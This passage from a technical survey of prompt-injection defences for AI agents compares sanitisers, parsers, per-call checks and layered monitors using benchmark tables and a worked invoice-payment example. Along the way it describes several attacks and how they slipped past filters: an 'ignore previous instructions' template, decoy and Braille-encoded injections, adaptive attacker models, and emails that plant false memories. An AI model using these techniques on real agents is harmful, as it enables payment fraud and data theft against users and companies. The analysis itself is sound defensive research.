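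Yu and colleagues tested the method on AgentDojo with three open models and three fixed attack templates. One template put "TODO" before the malicious request, another added an instruction to ignore previous instructions, and the third framed the request as an important message from the user. With both stages on, the average attack success rate was between 0% and 0.34%, depending on the model and the order of the stages. That average includes the attack-free run as a fourth result of zero, but without it every figure would still be below 0.5%.

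The results for Qwen3-32B under the "important message" attack, the strongest of the three, allow a comparison with marking and detecting:

| Treatment of tool results | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| None | 83.5% | 29.8% |
| Delimiters around the text | 80.4% | 25.1% |
| User's request repeated after the text | 77.3% | 16.9% |
| Classifier blocks suspicious text | 37.1% | 6.3% |
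| ParseData alone | 63.9% | 2.0% |
| CheckTool alone | 42.3% | 2.1% |
| ParseData, then CheckTool | 45.4% | 0.1% |

Marking kept the agent useful but stopped few attacks. The full method stopped nearly all of them, but the agent then completed little more than half as many tasks as before. Task completion also fell for the other models, from 61.9% to 48.5% for gpt-oss-120b and from 49.5% to 28.9% for Llama 3.1 70B. This was partly because CheckTool wrongly flagged ordinary data as a trigger and deleted it, especially with Qwen, which reasons at greater length.

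CheckTool would be awkward for the accounts assistant, because legitimate invoices also contain payment requests. The model might well respond to one by calling `pay_invoice`, and the runtime would then delete the request. False information can still get through. In an example from Yu and colleagues, the user wants to pay a Doctor John, and the injected text gives the attacker's email address as the doctor's. The agent calls only the tool it would have called anyway, so nothing looks wrong.

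A more basic weakness is that the extracting model reads the hostile text. In these tests it was also the same model as the agent, so an email that could fool one had a fair chance of fooling the other. The format and limits are written in natural language and the model decides whether a value meets them, so this method lacks the guarantees of a parser written in code.

### The tool-output firewall

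A simpler design has a model clean every tool result using one sanitising prompt. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) call this a tool-output firewall in *Indirect Prompt Injections*. The prompt contains the user's task and the tool's output, with instructions to keep the original format and remove any injection meant to make the agent do something unrelated to the task. The model returns the cleaned text, a brief explanation and a flag for whether the original was safe.

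They tested it with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, and again on a version of AgentDojo in which they had corrected several faults:

| Measure | Original, no defence | Original, sanitiser | Revised, no defence | Revised, sanitiser |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks | 34.2% | 0.01% | 34.3% | 0.01% |
| Tasks completed without an attack | 83.0% | 67.7% | 82.0% | 67.1% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 60.9% | 68.0% | 72.2% | 72.6% |

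(The paper's summary gives 74.1% instead of 67.7% for the sanitiser on the original benchmark without an attack, and doesn't explain the difference.)

The sanitiser stopped nearly every attack in both versions of the benchmark. In the original version, it also appeared to improve the agent's success on the user's own tasks under attack by about seven points. After the corrections, the improvement was less than one point, so most of it had come from faults in the benchmark. In some tasks, the injection had replaced information the agent needed, such as the amounts on a bill it had to pay, so even an agent that resisted the attack could not have completed them. Another task required a colleague's inbox to contain exactly one new message, so an agent failed if it sent the right message and an extra one.

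Bhagwatkar and colleagues found worse problems in another benchmark, Agent Security Bench. It added the attacker's tool to the set the agent had chosen, then counted any use of that tool as a successful attack. When they let the agent choose freely, attack success fell from about 70% to 9%. Llama 3.3 70B also got a perfect utility score on the benchmark by calling every available tool. They conclude that if one short prompt can score almost perfectly, the benchmarks need stronger attacks. This seems right, and it also means that the near-zero results are weaker evidence for the sanitiser than they appear.

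The sanitiser also deleted legitimate data. Once, it removed the user's own bank account number from a tool's output because the number didn't match the landlord's number in the request. Another time, it flagged an ordinary bill that asked for a bank transfer. These examples are hard to reconcile with the false-positive rate of zero that the paper reports elsewhere, though the examples use a slightly different prompt. Nine tasks repeatedly went worse with the sanitiser on, and Bhagwatkar and colleagues blame wrongful deletion for two of them and mistakes by the agent for the other seven.

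A companion filter, which removed unnecessary private data from outgoing tool calls, made stranger mistakes. When an agent tried to look up the prices of four hotels, the filter replaced the hotels with famous ones such as the Ritz Paris.

Cleaning every result is also slow, because the sanitiser has to write each one out again. Without attacks, the GPT-4o run took 1,697 seconds instead of 511, and average output per task rose from 303 to 1,675 tokens.

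### CausalArmor: cleaning only when the text drives an action

Kim, Parmar and colleagues (2026), in *CausalArmor*, try to avoid most of that cost. Their system does nothing until the agent proposes a privileged action, such as sending a message or moving money. It then measures how much the proposal depends on each part of the context. For a part *X*, which can be the user's request or one tool result, the influence is

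Δ(*X*) = [ log *P*(*Y* | *C*) − log *P*(*Y* | *C* without *X*) ] / |*Y*|

where *Y* is the proposed call, |*Y*| is its length in tokens, *C* is the whole context and *P* is the probability that a model would write *Y*. A smaller model calculates these probabilities in one batch, since many commercial models don't reveal theirs. A tool result *S* counts as suspicious if

Δ(*S*) > Δ(*U*) − *τ*

where *U* is the user's request and *τ* is a margin that the operator can raise to clean more often.

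Suppose an email contains an instruction for the accounts assistant to send the supplier list to a stranger. The model would probably still propose sending it if the clerk's request were removed, but almost certainly not if the email were removed. The email therefore has more influence on the proposal than the clerk's request does, so CausalArmor has a sanitiser clean the email. CausalArmor also replaces the agent's reasoning since that email with a placeholder, then has the agent decide again.

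Removing the reasoning matters because the agent may already have believed the attacker's story. In one case, the attacker presented a landlord's notice as a preview that the agent could unlock by sending a payment. The sanitiser removed this claim, but the agent's earlier reasoning still mentioned it, and the agent made the payment. Across all the tests, the average attack success rate was 0.29% when CausalArmor deleted the reasoning and 1.75% when it didn't.

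The AgentDojo tests used the "important message" template and two new ones, a fake preview notice and a fake database error. The table compares CausalArmor with PromptArmor, which has a language model check every tool result and remove any injection it finds.

| Agent's model | Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Time without an attack | Highest attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
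| Gemini 2.5 Flash | None | 53.6% | 1.00 | 32.5% |
| | PromptArmor | 41.2% | 2.44 | 0.6% |
| | CausalArmor | 56.3% | 1.30 | 0.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | None | 89.4% | 1.00 | 19.0% |
| | PromptArmor | 74.2% | 2.20 | 0.0% |
| | CausalArmor | 82.5% | 1.27 | 0.5% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | None | 92.8% | 1.00 | 8.9% |
| | PromptArmor | 77.3% | 1.78 | 0.3% |
| | CausalArmor | 86.6% | 1.22 | 0.1% |

CausalArmor was about as secure as cleaning everything, but it added much less delay and prevented far fewer tasks from being completed. The accounts assistant would probably benefit less. The payee and amount come from the invoice, so even a legitimate invoice would have a large influence on the exact tool call. CausalArmor might therefore clean the invoice before nearly every payment.

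Kim and colleagues also prove a bound on the risk. Over *T* steps with *M* possible harmful actions, the probability that the agent takes any of them is at most

*T* × *M* × e^−(*β* + *γ*)

Here *β* is how strongly the model favours the right action without the suspicious text, and *γ* is how strongly the cleaned text favours that action over a harmful one. The proof assumes that both are positive. Assuming a positive *γ* means assuming that the sanitiser has worked, so the bound can't show that it will.

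A harder test used DoomArena, in which an attacking model reads the conversation between a shopper and an agent and rewrites the shop's product data in response. With Gemini 3 Pro as the agent, CausalArmor reduced attack success from 88.9% to 3.7%. When there was no attack, the share of tasks completed fell from 73.6% to 71.0%. There is no sign that the attacker learned how CausalArmor worked. An attacker who did could try to spread an instruction over several tool results, so that no single result outweighed the user's request. Kim and colleagues think this would be difficult in ordinary language. They also advise operators to keep the identity of the smaller model secret, since an attacker could practise on a copy.

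### Attackers who adapt

AgentDojo's 949 attack cases combine many tasks and malicious goals, but a typical test uses the same attack wording in all of them. A filter that recognises this wording in one case will probably recognise it in the rest. Zero successful attacks is therefore strong evidence that the filter blocks that wording, but very little evidence that it blocks others. A real attacker can keep rewriting an email until one version works, then send that version to every company with the same filter.

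Using adaptive attacks, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, defeated twelve published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection. Later tests of filters and sanitisers point the same way. Bhagwatkar and colleagues attacked their own sanitiser in three stages on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, moving to the next stage only where the previous one had failed:

| Stage | Additional successes, firewall's sanitiser | Additional successes, PromptArmor |
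|---|---|---|
| Standard benchmark attack | 0.0% | 8.0% |
| Seven templates that disguise the instruction as harmless information | 12.5% | 64.0% |
| A model rewrites the attack over ten rounds, with feedback from the defence | 17.5% | 3.5% |
| Total | 30.0% | 75.5% |

In one successful attack, a web page contained an obvious injection as a decoy, followed by a second instruction labelled as a verified request from the user. The sanitiser removed the decoy but kept the second instruction, explaining that the label "appears to be legitimate authenticated user metadata". In another attack, the attacker wrote the standard injection in Braille characters. The sanitiser flagged the Braille as a possible danger but then translated it into English for the agent, which booked the attacker's choice of hotel.

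The attacking model in the third stage had access to the sanitiser's feedback, which an outside attacker normally wouldn't. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives its attacking model much less information. The model isn't told which defence is active, only how many times each injection worked. It ranks its earlier attempts, analyses why some did better and writes a new one. PIGuard, a classifier built to detect injections, blocked every fixed attack on a GPT-4o-mini agent but let through 28.0% of these adaptive attacks. Five defences had kept the success rate of fixed attacks on that agent near zero, but only Progent, which restricts the agent's tool calls, did the same against the adaptive ones.

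Attacks worked much more often when the user left the choice of action to the text, as in "follow the instructions in this file", probably because a filter then has no clear request to judge the text against. The clerk's request to deal with the new invoices is almost as open.

Writing new attacks also takes less human effort than it used to. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), groups of agents that shared notes found injections that worked even on the most robust models tested.

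### Filters made of fixed rules

Ordinary code can remove suspicious text without calling a model, and nothing written in an email can change its rules. But it catches only what its author anticipated, and broad rules damage legitimate text. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) examines attacks that use punctuation to make false data look like a separate, trusted field. Removing all the characters that could do this made the attacks succeed less often, but also corrupted web addresses and file paths that the agent needed.

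Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026), in *LivePI*, tested a rule-based filter in a more realistic setting. They ran OpenClaw on a real server with test email and chat accounts and a cryptocurrency wallet, then tried 169 attacks. Without a defence, 10.7% to 29.6% of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model. They then added a filter for phrases typical of injections and a policy that allowed each tool call, blocked it or sent it for human review. With GPT-5.3-Codex, the attack success rate fell from 27.2% to zero, and the policy interrupted nine of 899 calls on ordinary tasks.

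This result is weak evidence of how well the filter works, because Zhao and colleagues don't report a test of the filter without the policy. They also wrote seven of the policy's rules for the resources in their benchmark, and they tested the defence on only one model. They counted an attack as stopped if its tool call went to a human for review, which assumes the human would refuse the call.

In LivePI, all 15 attacks through group chats succeeded against all five undefended models, because OpenClaw passed messages from any group member to the model as if the user had written them. Many sanitisers would miss these messages because they clean only tool results.

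*SPILLWAY* (Lim, Chang and Lee, 2026) uses a rule-based sanitiser to support a check on where the agent's actions go. The check refuses a recipient or account found only in free text, unless a fixed rule allows it. A language model (the judge) can reconsider some refusals, for example when the user asked the agent to send a report to an address in some meeting notes. The sanitiser removes text that matches its rules, including forged chat messages, commands addressed to the agent and claims that a payee's account has changed. It also records what it removes, and the judge may not approve any destination in that record. In testing, when the user asked the agent to pay a bill, the judge approved a transfer to the attacker's account if the sanitiser was off, but was never consulted if it was on.

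SPILLWAY stopped every standard AgentDojo attack on three models and added less than one model call and under half a second per task. One of its rules matches AgentDojo's own template, so the sanitiser was bound to do well on that benchmark. The check on destinations is more reassuring because it doesn't depend on how the attacker words the email. Attacks from a model trained to write injections succeeded 0.6% of the time on average, but Lim and colleagues replayed them from a fixed set, so the attacker couldn't adapt them to SPILLWAY.

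For the accounts assistant, the rule about changed accounts would remove the attacker's new account number, but it would also remove an honest supplier's notice that it had changed banks. The check wouldn't stop the assistant from copying an attacker's false claim into a reply to a genuine supplier, because the destination would be legitimate. Only the sanitiser's rules could catch the claim, and a plain false statement might not match any of them.

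## How the layers work together

### One email through every layer

Suppose the company runs the accounts assistant with every layer on and opens a new session for each email. The parser gives the model a supplier number, an amount and two dates. Every tool has its own manifest. A per-call check accepts only accounts on file and payments up to £5,000. The budget allows £8,000 per session and £20,000 a day across all sessions. The assistant answers suppliers with one of eight standard replies, which the runtime sends to the address in the company's records.

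The attacker poses as supplier 417 and emails a reminder for £1,950. The email contains a new account number and a request for the full supplier list.

1. *Parsing.* The parser produces a record with supplier 417, £1,950 and the two dates. The new account number and the request for the list stay behind.
2. *Model decision.* The model sees what looks like an ordinary bill. It looks up supplier 417 and asks to pay £1,950 into the account on file.
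3. *Manifest.* The payment tool may contact the bank gateway and use the payment token, so the call can go ahead.
4. *Per-call check.* The account is on file and the amount is under the ceiling, so the check allows the payment.
5. *Budget.* The runtime reserves £1,950, which leaves £6,050 for the session.
6. *Egress limit.* The model picks the reply "we have received your invoice", and the runtime sends it to the real supplier 417.

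The attacker gets neither the money nor the list, but the company still pays £1,950 that it doesn't owe, although the real supplier may be puzzled by the reply and get in touch. Every layer worked as designed, but none compared the false bill with anything the company knew to be true, such as a purchase order. If supplier 417 had sent the bill itself, the fraud would have succeeded.

### Removing one layer at a time

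The table shows what happens if the company removes one layer and keeps the rest. It assumes that the model obeys any instruction it reads, so the model's own resistance does not count as a layer.

| Layer removed | Result of this email | Worst result of an attack aimed at the gap |
|---|---|---|
| None | £1,950 goes to supplier 417 by mistake | False bills of up to £5,000 per email, paid to genuine suppliers |
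| Parser | The check refuses the attacker's account, and the list stays inside | False payments of up to £8,000 per email to genuine suppliers |
| Manifest | No change | A flaw in one tool's code exposes the bank token and the supplier database |
| Per-call check | No change | If any text gets past the parser, up to £8,000 per email goes to the attacker |
| Budget | No change | False bills continue until the account is empty |
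| Egress limit | No change | If any text gets past the parser, the whole supplier list leaves in one reply |

For this email, the per-call check and the egress limit seem unnecessary because the parser has removed everything they would have caught. They matter when the parser has a bug, or when someone adds a text field to its schema. If the company removed both the parser and the per-call check, the attacker would receive £1,950.

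The manifest protects the other layers. A program with the stolen bank token could contact the bank directly, so the payment would bypass the runtime, which could neither check nor count it. The daily cap would still hold if the bank enforced it.

### Which layer affects which attack

The next table shows what each layer does on its own. "Prevented" means the layer stops the attack if it works as designed. "Bounded" means the attack can succeed, but the layer limits its size or route.

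| Attack | Parser | Manifest | Per-call check | Budget | Egress limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Payment to a new destination | Prevented | Untouched | Prevented | Bounded | Untouched |
| Permitted destination, false values | Bounded | Untouched | Bounded | Bounded | Untouched |
| Repeated small payments | Untouched | Untouched | Untouched | Bounded | Untouched |
| Data theft | Prevented | Bounded | Untouched | Untouched | Bounded |
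| Runaway cost | Bounded | Untouched | Untouched | Bounded | Untouched |
| False answer to the user | Bounded | Untouched | Untouched | Untouched | Untouched |

A payment to a new destination is the only case that two layers can each prevent. Only the budget can stop repeated small payments, because ten modest bills in ten separate emails would each pass the parser and the check.

The controls on tool calls can't stop a false answer, because giving one requires no forbidden call. If the clerk asks how much the company owes, the parser limits a false amount to the permitted range. But if the clerk asks for a summary of a complaint, the parser has to allow free text, so it no longer prevents data theft or limits what a false answer can claim.

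### Multiplying the failure rates

*A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) gives the usual advice, which is to use "multiple independent controls at different layers". The appeal of independence is easy to see with some made-up figures. Suppose 10% of attacks pass the parser, the model obeys 20% of those, and the checks permit 5% of the resulting calls. If the failures are independent, the share of attacks that succeed is

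0.10 × 0.20 × 0.05 = 0.001, or 0.1%

An attacker who knows about the layers would not send a typical attack. They might word the request as ordinary data and ask only for an action that the assistant may take. Again purely for illustration, 60% of these attacks might pass the parser, the model might act on 50% of those, and the checks would permit all of them:

0.60 × 0.50 × 1.00 = 0.30, or 30%

Correlation between the layers can't explain this jump by itself. At the original rates, the layers together would let through at most 5% of attacks, the rate of the strictest layer, even if they always failed on the same ones. The attacker reached 30% by choosing a kind of attack that every layer lets through more often.

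An average over many attacks can hide this. If only one attack in a hundred were of the well-chosen kind, the overall success rate would be only about 0.4%, but those attacks would account for three-quarters of the successes. A competent attacker would send only attacks of that kind.

### Do real layers fail independently?

In *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, Yang (2026) tested whether gates were independent, using 560 agent actions that a gate should block, such as deleting a production database. The gates were a set of 174 fixed text patterns and several language models acting as judges.

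| Pair of gates | Missed by each alone | Missed by both if independent | Missed by both in the test |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed rules and a judge | 13.4% and 10.5% | 1.4% | 1.3% |
| Two judges | 10.5% and 10.5% | 1.1% | 5.2% |

Yang expresses the difference as an equivalent number of independent layers,

*n* = ln *P* / ln *g*

where *P* is the share of actions that every gate misses and *g* is the geometric mean of the gates' separate miss rates. The two judges in the table are worth about 1.3 layers, while the rules and the judge are worth about two. Across all the pairs, two judges were worth 1.2 to 1.6 layers, and the rules with one judge were worth 1.8 to 2.1. A judge from a different company helped only a little.

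The judges may fail together because some cases are hard for all of them, or because they work in similar ways. Yang could not separate these explanations. Shared difficulty accounted for 32% to 62% of the excess joint failures, depending on the method.

A gate's accuracy alone was also a poor guide to its value in a stack. Extra rules for cloud services reduced the rule set's misses by a fifth, but caught nothing that a group of three judges had missed. Five of the study's conclusions also reversed depending on whether a verdict of "send to a human" counted as a success or a failure. One judge gave that verdict for 47 of the 560 actions. A company with nobody to review such cases should count them as misses.

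These results favour combining code with a language model over combining two language models. But nobody was trying to beat the gates, and Yang did not establish that the rules and the judges are independent, since the data allow for moderate correlation even between them. The rules also missed 53% of the dangerous actions in a cloud-computing set they were not written for. For the accounts assistant, code and a model would both miss a plausible false amount if neither had a purchase order to compare it with, so their failures on that attack would be perfectly correlated.

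### Experiments that remove layers

No published study appears to have tested manifests, session budgets and typed parsing together and then removed them one by one. The closest large experiment is *DefenseComposer* (Chen, Li and colleagues, 2026), which is by a different team from *Bounded Autonomy*. It tested 13 defences in 65 combinations on AgentDojo, plus an undefended agent, using Gemini 2.5 Flash. Each version faced 40 normal tasks and 240 attacks, and an attack counted as successful only if the agent achieved the attacker's exact goal.

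One combination had four defences: markers around untrusted text, two sanitisers (PromptArmor and CommandSans), and TaskShield, which checks proposed tool calls. The table also includes a tool filter, which restricts the tools the agent can use.

| Defences | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| None | 80.0% | 13.3% |
| All four | 5.0% | 0.0% |
| Four without the markers | 22.5% | 0.0% |
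| Four without PromptArmor | 10.0% | 0.4% |
| Four without TaskShield | 52.5% | 2.5% |
| Four without CommandSans | 57.5% | 0.4% |
| Tool filter alone | 52.5% | 4.2% |
| CommandSans alone | 72.5% | 8.8% |
| Tool filter and CommandSans | 52.5% | 3.3% |
| Tool filter and delimiters | 77.5% | 0.4% |

The four-defence agent resisted every attack but finished only two of its 40 normal tasks. Its perfect security score means very little, because an agent that can do almost nothing is also hard to hijack. Removing CommandSans let the agent complete 21 more tasks, but one of 240 attacks succeeded. The drop in completed tasks was partly specific to the model, since Qwen-Max and DeepSeek-V4-Pro completed about half of their tasks with the same four defences.

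The tool filter combined with the CommandSans sanitiser comes closest to the accounts assistant's layers, because it both limits tools and sanitises what they return. Adding CommandSans to the filter reduced successful attacks only from 4.2% to 3.3%. This is weak evidence about a typed parser, because CommandSans edits free text and leaves the rest in place.

Chen and colleagues then attacked three of the combinations with text written for that exact set of defences. The attack success rate rose from 0.4% to 8% for the tool filter with delimiters, from zero to 8% for the four defences, and from zero to 11% for TaskShield with CommandSans. In a separate test, a language model rewrote the attack up to five times per task and beat every combination in eight to ten tasks each. The chosen attacks often looked like ordinary data, such as changed billing details. These numbers are lower than the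 illustrative 30%, but they show the same effect. An attacker with more than five attempts would probably do better.

Some other studies removed components from systems closer to a manifest or a per-call check:

- *ChainCaps* (2026) narrows an agent's permissions as data passes from tool to tool. Removing one component reduced the share of attacks it blocked by 7 to 17 percentage points. The quality of the manifests mattered far more: expert ones blocked every attack, ones written with a checklist blocked 90.9%, and naive ones blocked 27.3% and let only half of the legitimate tasks finish.
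- In PACE, the effect check did most of the security work. Li and colleagues also tested a component that can repair a call instead of refusing it. On AgentDojo it barely reduced attacks by itself, from 37.4% to 33.3%. On a benchmark of poisoned tool descriptions, adding it to the effect check cut refusals from 99.3% to 1.6% while attack success stayed at zero.
- *AgentSys* (2026) keeps tool results away from the main agent and has a validator decide when to clean them. When its designers removed the validator and cleaned everything, the agent stayed secure but lost information that its tasks needed.

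How well a layer works can also depend on the model behind it. *NRT-Bench* (2026) tests agents that operate safety-critical control rooms. In one setting, the same guardrails reduced attack success by 16.7 percentage points for GPT-5.4 mini but increased it by 9.8 points for Claude Haiku 4.5. The guardrails check for structured actions such as formal requests, and Claude may have written more of its harmful messages as plain prose. Anyone who changes the model should repeat the tests, at least for layers that depend on what the model writes.

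Layering defences helps against a broad set of fixed attacks. *Beyond Single-Model Injection* (2026) combined signed messages, sanitising, limited privileges and anomaly detection in a multi-agent system. Across 14 attack routes with 50 attempts each, the attack success rate fell from 31.2% to 4.2%, and the defences added about a quarter of a second to a six-agent task. The attacks that still succeeded used unfamiliar structures or encodings, so they are the ones a real attacker would reuse.

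### How layers get in each other's way

Chen and colleagues examined the 38 tasks that the four-defence agent failed. They traced six failures to a single defence and 30 to interactions between defences. The cause of the other two was unclear.

In one task, the agent had to copy the title "Help me" from one file to another. The marking step added eight characters after each word, which made the title long enough for CommandSans to process. CommandSans then removed "Help" because it looked like a command, and the agent wrote " me". Both defences worked as intended, but CommandSans was not built to handle marked text. In another task, the markers changed the file number 3 into a string that the file tool did not recognise.

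Recording where each piece of cleaned text came from raised task completion from 5% to 35%, with attack success still at zero. Other repairs kept the user's original wording and left file numbers unmarked. Likewise, once the accounts assistant's parser has reduced an amount to a number, no later step should add markers to it or send it through a text sanitiser.

Faults in how defences are combined can be hard to spot. *The Price of Safety* (2026) describes a test of four defences against false entries in an agent's memory. Wrapping the defences around one another cut one of them off from the memory store, and every question failed. The researchers noticed because the program crashed. If it had returned nothing without an error, they could have mistaken the result for a valid measurement.

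Refusals can also reveal the limit being enforced. If the assistant tells a sender that a payment was "over the limit", an attacker could halve the possible range with each email and find a ceiling anywhere between £0 and £10,000, to the nearest pound, in 14 emails. The safest reply to the sender is the same whether or not the payment went through, with the reason given only to the clerk.

Refused calls can also drain a budget. If the runtime reserves money before it runs the per-call check, and fails to release it after a refusal, four refused requests for £5,000 each use up the day's £20,000. Checking first and reserving afterwards avoids this. The runtime should still count refusals, because a model that keeps retrying costs money and gives an attacker more chances to find a call that works. A separate limit of, say, three refusals per session would stop the retries without reducing the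 budget for real invoices.

People can weaken the layers too. A manager might add a "notes" field to the invoice schema, thinking that the eight standard replies would stop any data from leaving. A colleague might later allow free-text replies, thinking that the parser removes all instructions. Either change would be fairly safe if the other layer stayed strict, but together they would give an attacker a way to instruct the model and a way to receive the supplier list.

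### How layers help each other

The parser makes the later checks much easier. Code can compare 1950.00 with a purchase order, but it can't easily check "last month's balance plus the usual surcharge". A supplier number also lets the runtime look up the approved account itself, so it doesn't use the attacker's account number.

A filter can help even when it is too unreliable to decide anything alone. In the defence that Zhao and colleagues built for OpenClaw, the text filter only flags suspicious passages. The tool policy then checks those flags along with the proposed call and whether the session has handled untrusted content. The accounts assistant could likewise refer a payment to the clerk when the email behind it contains text that looks like instructions. A false alarm would then take a minute of the clerk's time instead of deleting part of a real invoice.

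### Two safe permissions that leak together

Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026) argue in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* that defences against single weaknesses rarely combine well. They list finding defences against prompt injection that do combine well as an open problem. PlanTERS is a small, exact example of the difficulty.

Dongol's email summariser holds a private account number. If it can read the inbox but can't fetch web pages, a hostile email can instruct the model, but the model has no way to send the number out. If it can fetch pages but can't read the inbox, it could send the number out but never receives the instruction. Both versions are relatively secure, meaning that injection adds no leaks. An agent with both permissions leaks the account number. Reviewing each tool's manifest separately would not reveal this, so someone has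 to review the manifests together.

Removing a permission can also change the verdict from secure to insecure. Suppose an agent's plan sends a secret to an outsider, and an injection makes the agent fetch a web address containing the same secret. The agent counts as relatively secure because the outsider would have received the secret anyway. If the operator removes the send tool, the planned disclosure stops but the injected one continues. The agent now counts as insecure, even though it leaks no more than before. The operator's change was too narrow because it left the attacker's route open.

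Dongol draws six rules for designing a monitor from the proofs:

1. *Withdraw the tools that an injection could call as soon as the agent reads untrusted content.* The session that reads an invoice email should not have the payment tool.
2. *Control what the agent reads as well as what it calls.* In one example, an injected program chooses which page to read according to a secret. Whoever runs the server can learn the secret from that choice, even if the agent never sends a message.
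3. *Approve exact calls, not tools.* The clerk should approve £1,200 to a named supplier and not "one payment". The proof assumes that the attacker can't see the timing of messages.
4. *Spend budgets before untrusted content arrives.* The assistant should send the accountant's report before it opens the new mail.
5. *Return withdrawn tools only in a fresh session.* Otherwise the model can still obey an old email once the tools are back.
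6. *Keep refusals from revealing arguments.* In another example, an injection calls an internal tool that works only if the user has switched on a private setting. An attacker who can see the error message learns the setting.

The rules address leaks. They are also sensible for the accounts assistant, but without a guarantee, because that assistant has no fixed plan.

The assistant has to read an invoice before paying it, which seems to conflict with the first and fourth rules. Reading the invoice in one session and paying it in a new one avoids the conflict, but only if the saved record contains nothing but checked numbers. If somebody adds a text field to the record, the paying session also reads untrusted content and would lose its payment tool under the first rule.

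## Why prompt injection remains possible

The layers around the accounts assistant limit what happens after the model obeys an attacker, but they don't make the model less likely to obey. Mellafe Zuvic measured the two separately, using a mock payment agent that received a fraudulent message worded like a routine finance update. Two cheap models, GPT-4o-mini and GLM-4.5-air, each attempted the unauthorised payout in all ten trials, and ScopeGate denied every attempt.

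*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* expresses the difference as

Induced(*c*, *O*) ⇏ Permitted(*c*)

where *c* is a proposed call and *O* is something the agent has read. Content can lead the model to propose a call, but this doesn't give the call permission to run. The paper's own system, SARA, looks for that permission just before a tool acts. Attacks succeeded at most 0.63% of the time in its four main tests. That figure leaves out the calls SARA refused, so it doesn't show how often the model obeyed.

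A typed parser is a partial exception because it removes most of the text the model could obey. But it doesn't change how the model treats any text that gets through.

### Harms the layers leave

An attacker may succeed using only actions the agent is allowed to take. OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026) describes how GPT-Red, a model trained to write injections, attacked an AI agent that runs a vending machine in OpenAI's office. The model got the agent to cut an expensive item's price to $0.50, order another item worth over $100 to sell at the same price, and cancel a customer's order. Since $0.50 was the lowest price the agent could set, a check on the minimum price would have allowed that price. AgentBound failed to stop the redirected cryptocurrency transfers for much the same reason.

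SC Media's *After the identity fix*, a commentary by Nik Kale, proposes tying each tool call to the user's request. Software outside the model signs a record of the request and the operation it needs, and the tool refuses any other operation. An agent asked to summarise a PDF then could not change a customer's email address. This would help the accounts assistant less, because the attacker wants it to make a payment, which the clerk also asks it to do.

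An attacker can also do harm through a false summary, without any tool call. Suppose a complaint from a supposed supplier makes the assistant tell the clerk that supplier 417 has changed banks. The clerk has the authority to change the supplier records, and so can serve as a second deputy for the attacker. If the clerk believes the summary and updates the records, the per-call check will approve the attacker's account from then on.

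The attacker can also bias a choice. If the clerk asks which of three quotes to accept, one bidder could hide text in its quote to make the model recommend that quote. All three answers are permitted, so no rule about permitted actions can detect the bias. Code could compare the prices, but the clerk probably asked a model because the decision depends on more than price.

Other injections cause harm in a later session. In a test from *ZoneClaw* (2026), a user asks an agent to read new email and update its memory file. One email contains a false rule that all outgoing mail is copied to a certain address for auditing. A monitor checks the rule before the agent saves it, but allows it because of its stated compliance purpose. When the user later asks the agent to write to a colleague, the agent adds that address as a hidden recipient. A per-call check would have to cover hidden recipients as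 well as the main address.

Zhang, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell*, trained a model to plant such memories with a single email. An attack counted as successful only if the agent saved the false memory, gave the user no sign of it, and acted on it in a later session. The attack succeeded in 87.5% of 56 test cases against OpenClaw with GPT-5.4, and in 71.4% against an agent built on Claude Code's toolkit with Sonnet 4.6.

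### How often current models obey

Laboratories publish safety test results for new models in *system cards*. The consultancy Digital Applied (2026) reports that, according to the June 2026 card for Claude Fable 5, adaptive attacks on coding tasks succeeded 0.41% of the time. According to Anthropic, the closely related Mythos 5 had the best result yet on a prompt injection benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan.

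Anthropic later commissioned the firm Trajectory Labs to test auto mode, Claude Code's automated approval system. Willison, the programmer who proposed the dual-LLM pattern, reports the result but has some doubts about it. The table lists these figures alongside OpenAI's and those for the memory attacks.

| Model | Attack | Attempts | Successful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5, in auto mode | 72 scenarios with injected content | 720 | 0 |
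| GPT-5.6 Sol | GPT-Red's direct injections | Not stated | 0.05% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Adaptive attacks on coding tasks | 200 per scenario | 0.41% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Adaptive attacks on coding tasks | 200 per scenario | 2.09% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Text imitating the model's own reasoning | Not stated | Under 10% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | One email plants a false memory | 56 | 71.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | One email plants a false memory | 56 | 87.5% |

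Success rates for prompt injection vary so much by attack that no single number can summarise a model's resistance. GPT-Red's direct injections almost never succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol overall, but OpenAI gives only "below 10%" for the attacks that imitate the model's reasoning. Success rates for those attacks reached more than 95% against GPT-5.1. For content in browsers and developer tools, OpenAI separately reports a pass rate above 97% on several benchmarks. The memory attacks targeted older models, and saving a plausible fact may also be harder for a model to identify as suspicious than sending a file.

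Zero successes in 720 attempts is a very good result, but even if the attempts were independent, the true success rate could be as high as about 0.4%. The result also covers only one product. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, describes PleaseFix, a family of attacks on five AI browsers that researchers presented at the Black Hat conference in 2026. With Claude in Chrome, a single request to summarise an inbox led the agent to send out the user's Gmail and share their Google Drive. *Yet another research breaks the hype bubble for AI browsers* (Priyadarshini, 2026) reports an earlier test that found four of seven AI browsers vulnerable to attacks that extract personal data.

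All these models date from mid-2026 or earlier, and Anthropic has since released Mythos 5.2, as Mowshowitz (2026), in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*, describes.

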